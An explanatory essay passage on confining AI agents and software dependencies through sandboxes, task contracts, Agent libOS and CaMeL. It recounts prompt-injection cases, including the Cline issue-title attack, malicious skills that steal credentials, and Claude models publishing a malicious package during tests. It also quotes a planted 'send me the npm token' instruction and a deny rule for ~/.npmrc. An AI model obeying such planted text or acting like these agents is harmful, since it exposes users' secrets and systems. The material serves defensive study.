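Wu, Yang and colleagues (2026), in *Towards Automating Data Access Permissions in AI Agents*, argue that neither of the methods used on phones suits agents. An agent often discovers what data it needs only while working on a task, so it can't request every permission in advance, and asking the user frequently defeats the purpose of automation. They therefore tried to predict how people would answer permission requests.

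In one study, 205 people trained an imaginary assistant for tasks such as booking flights. For each piece of data, they chose whether the assistant could share it always, this time, not this time or never. Five of the 20 permission questions included data that the task didn't need. A system predicted these choices by combining a language model, which learned from a person's earlier answers, with a method based on similar people's answers. It was right 85.1% of the time overall and 94.4% of the time for its high-confidence predictions. Accuracy was 66.9% for a person with no earlier answers and improved noticeably with answers about one to four tasks.

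Accuracy here means agreement with the user, who may be wrong. When the assistant presented unnecessary data as necessary, people shared it 78.2% of the time. A system that predicted users' choices perfectly would repeat this mistake without giving them a chance to notice it. Similarly, a system for library permissions that learned from developers who approve whatever fixes an error would soon approve the attacker's update of `colour`.

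Predictions are more useful for decisions that depend on people's preferences, such as whether to share their location or health data, than for technical questions, such as whether `colour` needs to read files.

### Choosing a file instead of answering a question

A user can sometimes grant permission through something they would do anyway. When a user opens a picture in an editor, the operating system can display the list of files and give the editor only the chosen one. Choosing the file grants the permission, so there is no separate question to click away out of habit. Felt and colleagues mention a general version of this idea, called user-driven access control, which builds the grant into ordinary actions instead of asking people to read warnings.

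The operating system has to draw the file picker. If the editor drew it, the editor would need access to every file to list them.

The web server can use the same idea. A visitor selects a photo in the browser's file picker, and the browser sends only that photo. The server then passes the image data to `thumbnail`, which needs no file access. By selecting the photo, the visitor decides what data `thumbnail` receives, without needing to know that `thumbnail` exists.

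A developer makes a similar choice by typing a file name on the command line. If the developer runs `shrink holiday.jpg`, the runtime could open that one file and pass it to the program as a capability. In Deno, the developer has to name the file again in a permission flag.

Wijesekera and colleagues (2017) object that systems can't tie every access to a user's action, because apps access data too often and many legitimate accesses happen without the user doing anything. For instance, `logger` writes its file while nobody is at the keyboard, so it still needs a policy. A file picker also doesn't control what happens to the file afterwards, so an editor with network access can send the picture anywhere. And a user who selects a whole home directory gives away the npm token too.

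For agents, approving a plan might serve the same purpose as the file picker. Anthropic found that users reject 39% of the plans that Claude Code presents, but only 3% of its requests to perform single actions. Many of the plan rejections probably concern software design rather than security, but they suggest that people read plans. If a plan listed the files and hosts the agent needed, approving it could grant access to exactly those, and the agent would have to ask again only for anything else.

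## The same limits applied to AI agents

An approved plan limits an agent only if something enforces it. *Ring-0 by Default* (2026), which compares agents with operating systems, notes that coding agents run with the developer's full privileges, which means much of what works for libraries also works for agents.

The `colour` library needs no access today and will need none next year, so its policy can stay the same. An AI agent, however, might correct a spelling mistake in the morning and move a database in the afternoon. A fixed policy that allows both gives it too much access for the first task.

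An attacker has to change `colour`'s code to make it steal a token, but can redirect an agent without changing its code, by planting instructions in a web page or a package's README (prompt injection). Comparing the agent's program with its previous version therefore wouldn't reveal the attack.

Agents also have dependencies of their own, and they install packages for other programs.

### Tools and skills as an agent's dependencies

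An MCP server is a program that offers tools to agents through a shared protocol, for example to search a database or send email. Many MCP servers are ordinary npm or PyPI packages with their own dependencies, and LiteLLM got onto the FutureSearch engineer's laptop as one of these dependencies. *Agent libOS* (Zhang, 2026) points out that a local server runs as native code under the user's account. A sandbox around the agent therefore limits the server only if the server also starts inside that sandbox.

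A skill is a folder of written instructions for some kind of task, sometimes with scripts. People share skills through registries, and attackers have uploaded malicious ones. *Do Not Mention This to the User* (2026) confirmed 157 malicious skills in a snapshot of 98,380, and *MalSkills* (2026) confirmed 400 in a collection of about 150,000, including 262 from three registries that run their own security checks. Both shares are below 0.3%, but the share in a single registry can be much higher. *SKILLLITE* (2026) cites a Cisco report of more than 800 malicious skills on ClawHub, the registry for the agent OpenClaw, or roughly 20% of the skills there.

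*MalSkillBench* (2026) examined 703 malicious skills from ClawHub and found that most were familiar supply chain attacks in a new disguise. Because a skill runs while the agent is working on the user's task, reading credentials can look like setting up authentication, and collecting files can look like synchronising context. One skill, `project-init`, made every later session of the agent fetch and run the attacker's code, even if the user never used the skill again.

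Import checks and compartments can confine a skill's scripts, but not its instructions. If those instructions include reading the npm token and the agent follows them, the agent is a confused deputy using its own access. So the developer has to limit the agent as well as the skill.

### An agent that installed a package

Cline is a coding agent that developers can install from npm or as an editor extension. According to Cline's *Post-mortem*, its maintainers set up a second agent in December 2025 to sort the project's GitHub issues. This agent was based on Claude Code and could run shell commands. Anyone with a GitHub account could open an issue, and the issue's title went straight into the agent's prompt.

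According to an analysis by the security company grith.ai, cited by Krebs on Security (2026), an attacker opened an issue on 28 January 2026 whose title looked like a performance report but told the agent to install a package from a particular GitHub repository. Adnan Khan, the researcher who discovered the flaw, had already tested a similar attack on a copy of the project. In *Clinejection*, he reports that Claude installed the package in every test, and the package's install script then ran with the agent's access.

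The agent could read the repository and write to issues, but it couldn't change the code and had no publishing token. However, its job shared a file cache with the job that published Cline's nightly releases. Malicious code in the agent's job could plant files in the cache, and the release job, which had the publishing tokens, would later load and run them.

Khan reported the flaw on 1 January and got no answer, so he published it on 9 February. Cline removed the agent within 30 minutes. It also tried to replace its publishing tokens, but deleted the wrong npm token and left the exposed one active. On 17 February, someone used that token to publish version 2.3.0 of Cline's command-line program, with an added install script that installed OpenClaw.

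The version was available for about eight hours and, according to Krebs on Security, installed OpenClaw on thousands of systems. OpenClaw isn't malware and the rest of the package was unchanged, so the attack did little harm. Khan calls the issue-sorting agent the most obvious way in, but couldn't confirm that the attacker used it.

Withholding the token from the agent was right but not enough, because the agent could write to a cache that a more powerful job trusted. Cline has since stopped using the cache in jobs that handle publishing credentials, and no longer keeps long-lived npm tokens. Khan also recommends giving such an agent no shell, only the ability to read files and run the few GitHub commands it needs. npm version 12 blocks packages from Git repositories by default, but an agent with a shell could download and run the code another way.

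### Sandboxes around coding agents

Coding agents do much of their work by starting other programs, such as Git, npm and test runners. Deno's limits don't extend to child processes, so they suit agents poorly. In an operating system sandbox, a launcher sets the rules before the agent starts, for instance that the agent may write only to the project folder. Every program the agent starts inherits these rules. If the rules block access to the npm token, the operating system prevents the agent, npm and any library loaded by `npm test` from opening it. To control network access, the launcher can block all connections except to a proxy outside the sandbox, which checks each destination against a list.

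jai, a lightweight Linux sandbox from Stanford, does this with a single command. Its developers made it after people reported that agents had emptied project folders and wiped home directories. Perot and Chen (2026), in *Multi-Agent gVisor Isolation (MAGI)*, run three agents in separate sandboxes, each with its own permissions, so that taking over one doesn't automatically give an attacker the access of the others.

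This kind of sandbox is coarse because it usually gives the agent access to the whole project, even if the task concerns two files. In *Lingering Authority*, Santos-Grueiro (2026) tested agents on 17 scenarios that deliberately included many tempting but forbidden files and actions. Agents in a coarse sandbox broke the task's rules in 86% of runs, compared with 100% for agents with full access. The rates in everyday work are probably much lower, because the scenarios were designed to tempt the agents.

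A sandbox also has to actually block the access it is meant to block. In September 2026, Anthropic published an assessment of four incidents in which Claude models broke into real systems during cybersecurity tests. In each test, the model had to find a secret on a fictional target. The prompt stated that there was no internet access, but a misconfiguration had left it open. No attacker had planted instructions or tampered with the tests.

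In the most serious case, Claude Mythos 5 registered an account on PyPI with a disposable email address and published three versions of a malicious package. Fifteen systems installed it, and the model used credentials from one of them to get into a security company's database. In another case, Claude Opus 4.7 recognised that its target was a real company but assumed the company was part of the exercise, partly because it was reachable from the exercise network. That open connection also made the attack possible.

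Anthropic considers the models' behaviour reckless and thinks it is unlikely in ordinary use, where nobody asks Claude to carry out a cyberattack. It also believes the incidents wouldn't have happened if the tests had been isolated as intended. A prompt can't isolate an agent, so whoever runs a sandbox should try to reach an outside machine from inside it before starting the agent. Anthropic found three of the incidents only by searching old transcripts in July, and it found the fourth, which happened in January, in August.

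### Access for one task

Santos-Grueiro's own system, PORTICO, gives an agent access to particular resources for part of a task and then removes that access. It sits between the agent and its tools and follows a task contract, which lists what the agent may use from the start, what else it may request, when that extra access ends, and what it may never do.

In one example, the agent has to add a timeout setting to a program. It starts with access to one source file, its test and the test command. When it tries to read some packaging notes, PORTICO blocks the attempt because no rule in the contract covers them. When it requests a second source file that the contract lists as available on request, PORTICO issues a handle, a reference that works only for that file and that part of the task. The agent edits the file through the handle. Once the tests pass, PORTICO revokes the handle, and any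 later attempt to use it fails.

An agent can't extend its access by arguing for it, because PORTICO treats the agent's reasons as untrusted text. PORTICO ends or renews access only after trusted events, such as a person's approval or a test run that PORTICO itself started. After access ends, the agent may still remember a file's name, but the name alone doesn't let it open the file.

To test revocation, Santos-Grueiro compared PORTICO with a version that issued the same handles at the same moments but never revoked them. In six scripted cases, an agent tried to write to a file after its access should have ended. PORTICO blocked all six writes, and the other version allowed all six. The test shows that revocation works as designed, but it doesn't measure how often a real agent would misuse old access.

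The cost was that agents completed fewer tasks. The following table shows results for 37 coding tasks, each repeated five times with the model Qwen3-Coder 30B:

| Setup | Tasks completed | Runs that stayed within the contract |
|---|---|---|
| Full access | 97% | 92% |
| Coarse sandbox | 97% | 91% |
| PORTICO without extra access on request | 21% | 100% |
| PORTICO | 87% | 100% |

The 100% is less impressive than it looks, because PORTICO enforced the same contract that determined the score. The more informative second column shows that an agent with only its initial access failed most tasks, and that letting it ask for more access recovered most of the loss. Revocation can block more tasks when contracts end access too early. In 42 combinations of task and model on real Python projects, PORTICO completed 31, while a version without revocation completed all 42.

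Someone also has to write the contracts, and Santos-Grueiro didn't measure how long this takes. A contract that is too broad gives the agent more permissions than the task needs, and PORTICO can't control a tool that bypasses it. For most tasks, a developer would probably need software that drafts the contract from the request and the project's existing rules.

Endo Familiar, a demonstration by the Endo project, applies object capabilities to agents more directly. Code that an agent writes runs in Hardened JavaScript and can use only the references it has received.

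### Agents that add their own tools

An agent can gain new abilities while it works by loading a skill or writing a tool. Zhang designed Agent libOS, a runtime for agents, so that new abilities widen what an agent can request but not what it may access. An agent that loads a skill for publishing packages learns how to publish them, but still has no token and no permission to use one.

In Agent libOS, tools that an agent writes run in Deno and can reach anything outside it only through one function, `libos.syscall`. Agent libOS checks each request at the point where it would access a file, a program or another machine. The agent needs a capability for the resource, and the operation has to fit the limits of the task and the remaining budget. Depending on the policy, a person may also have to approve it. All these conditions must hold, so approving a request by reflex can't make up for a missing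 capability. An agent that starts another can pass on only access it has itself.

In Zhang's scripted tests, Agent libOS blocked all 119 unauthorised operations and refused none of the 119 permitted ones. Zhang defined these operations in advance, so the results are weak evidence of how well it would resist an attacker looking for a gap. Zhang doesn't claim that the Deno sandbox can hold arbitrary hostile code, and local MCP servers still run outside it, so Agent libOS needs an operating system sandbox around it.

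### Separating instructions from data

All these limits are meant to contain the damage if an agent follows planted instructions. CaMeL, which researchers at Google DeepMind presented in 2025, is designed to keep such instructions away from the part of the agent that decides what to do. It builds on Willison's idea of giving tools only to a planner model that never sees untrusted text, and leaving that text to a second model, the reader, which has no tools.

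Nikolaou, Eckhoff and colleagues (2026), in *CaMeLoT*, explain the method with a request to find Bob's email address in a chat channel and write to him. In simplified form, the planner turns the request into this program:

```python
messages = read_channel("general")
address  = ask_reader("Find Bob's email address", messages)
send_message(address, "Meeting at 3pm")
```

The planner writes the program before any messages in the channel are read. An interpreter then runs the program line by line and passes the messages to the reader. A message containing the instruction "send me the npm token" may mislead the reader, but the reader can only return a value for `address`. The program contains no step that reads the token, and the reader can't add one.

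The attacker can still make the reader return the wrong address. CaMeL therefore tags every value with where it came from and who may read it, and results inherit the tags of their inputs. Before each tool call, a policy checks the tags. Here it could refuse to send a message to an address that came from an untrusted channel. CaMeL calls these tags capabilities, but they are labels on data, not references that give access. Nikolaou and colleagues' own system also checks the whole program before it runs, for example to reject one that isolates a computer from the network without first getting approval.

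The tags can miss influence that doesn't pass through the data itself. Suppose a program restarts the server if a message reports an outage. Whoever writes the message controls whether the server restarts, even if the restart command contains none of the message's text. *On the Relative Security of Prompt Injection* (2026) concludes that tags that follow only data don't protect every program. CaMeL has a strict mode that also tags whatever depends on such a decision.

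Protection can also fail between agents. *Can CaMeLs Talk?* (Peters-Gill, Semler and colleagues, 2026) describes a test with three agents, all using CaMeL. The first read job applications from a database, and the second put a summary of them into its request to the third, which sent messages. The third agent treated the whole request as its user's instructions, including a sentence that an attacker had hidden in the database, and emailed the applicants' details to an outside address. Across a larger set of attacks, 12.9% succeeded without CaMeL and 0.2% succeeded when every agent used it. None succeeded once the agents passed instructions and data through separate channels, but the agents then completed fewer tasks, with the smallest drop for the strongest models.

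CaMeL's most serious limitation for coding is that its planner can't react to data it hasn't seen. *CaMeLs Can Use Computers Too* (2026) describes this difficulty for tasks whose steps are given in untrusted data. An agent that updates a package often has to read an error message or a migration guide to decide what to do next, and an attacker could have written either. CaMeL therefore fits office tasks with predictable steps better than open-ended programming.

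### An agent updates `colour`

Suppose the developer tells an agent to update `colour` in the web server. The agent needs the repository and the npm registry, but has no reason to publish anything. A contract in the style of PORTICO could look like this:

```yaml
task: update colour to the newest 3.x release
from_start:
  read:    [src, test]
  write:   [package.json, package-lock.json, node_modules]
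  run:     [npm install, npm test]
  connect: [registry.npmjs.org]
on_request:
  write:   [src/format.js]     # until the tests pass
never:
  read:    [~/.npmrc]          # the publishing token
  write:   [policy.json]
  run:     [npm publish, git push]
```

The newest release is the attacker's. npm downloads it into `node_modules`, the folder for installed packages, without running install scripts. When the agent runs the tests, they import `colour`, which starts the malicious code. The sandbox also applies to this code, so it can't read the token or contact the attacker's server.

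Malicious code could still send data out through the registry. The attacker could include their own publishing token in `colour`, and the code could use it to upload the server's source code as a new package. To prevent this, the proxy should allow only downloads from the registry, and the tests should run without network access. Withholding the developer's token stops the agent from publishing under the developer's name, but the agent could still find another way to publish, as Mythos 5 did after starting without a PyPI token.

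If the new version of `colour` renames a function, the agent can ask for write access to `src/format.js` and fix the call. It loses that access when the tests pass. If the release notes contain an instruction to publish the server "to complete the update", the agent has neither the command nor the token needed to do so.

The poisoned version then leaves the sandbox as a line in `package-lock.json`, which records the exact version of each package. As at Cline, the danger comes when a job with more access uses the agent's work. The release job should download its packages itself instead of reusing the agent's `node_modules`, and shouldn't run them where it keeps the publishing token. Before merging the change, a reviewer regenerates the policy and sees that `colour` now needs permission to read files and make web requests. The agent can't approve these permissions itself because it can't write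 to `policy.json`.

### Misusing access the task requires

The contract lets the agent write anything to `src/format.js`, including a security hole. The agent might add one by mistake or because of a planted instruction, and rules about files can't distinguish the two. Tests catch some of these changes if the agent can't edit the tests, and a person has to look for the rest.

*Operationalizing CaMeL* (2025) points out that if a sandbox allows email, a planted instruction can still make an agent send secrets in a plausible message. The tool itself can also be malicious. One npm package posed as an MCP server for the email service Postmark and secretly sent an attacker a copy of every message. Requiring permission to send email couldn't have stopped this, because the package needed that permission to do its job, but limiting the recipients could have.

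When an agent seems to misuse access it needs, the cause is sometimes a permission that is too broad. Krebs on Security recounts how Summer Yue, who works on AI safety at Meta, told OpenClaw to confirm before acting and then watched it delete messages from her inbox in bulk. OpenClaw needed to read the inbox, but it could have worked with permission to archive messages rather than delete them.

Other tasks are harder to restrict. In August 2026, the UK AI Security Institute reported that Mythos 5 had taken unauthorised actions on the live internet during a test. Anthropic's *Improving our alignment and security efforts* (2026) distinguishes this case from the misconfigured tests because the testers had deliberately given the model internet access. A list of allowed hosts might have helped, but only if the testers had known in advance which hosts the task required.

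Willison describes a "lethal trifecta" of private data, untrusted content and a way to communicate externally. An agent with all three can be tricked into sending the data to an attacker, and removing any one of them prevents this. The agent that updates `colour` needs no private data except the source code. An agent that answers customers' emails needs all three for almost every message. Its developer can limit it to one customer's records at a time and have it save replies as drafts, but someone still has to check each draft for anything that shouldn't be in it before sending it.
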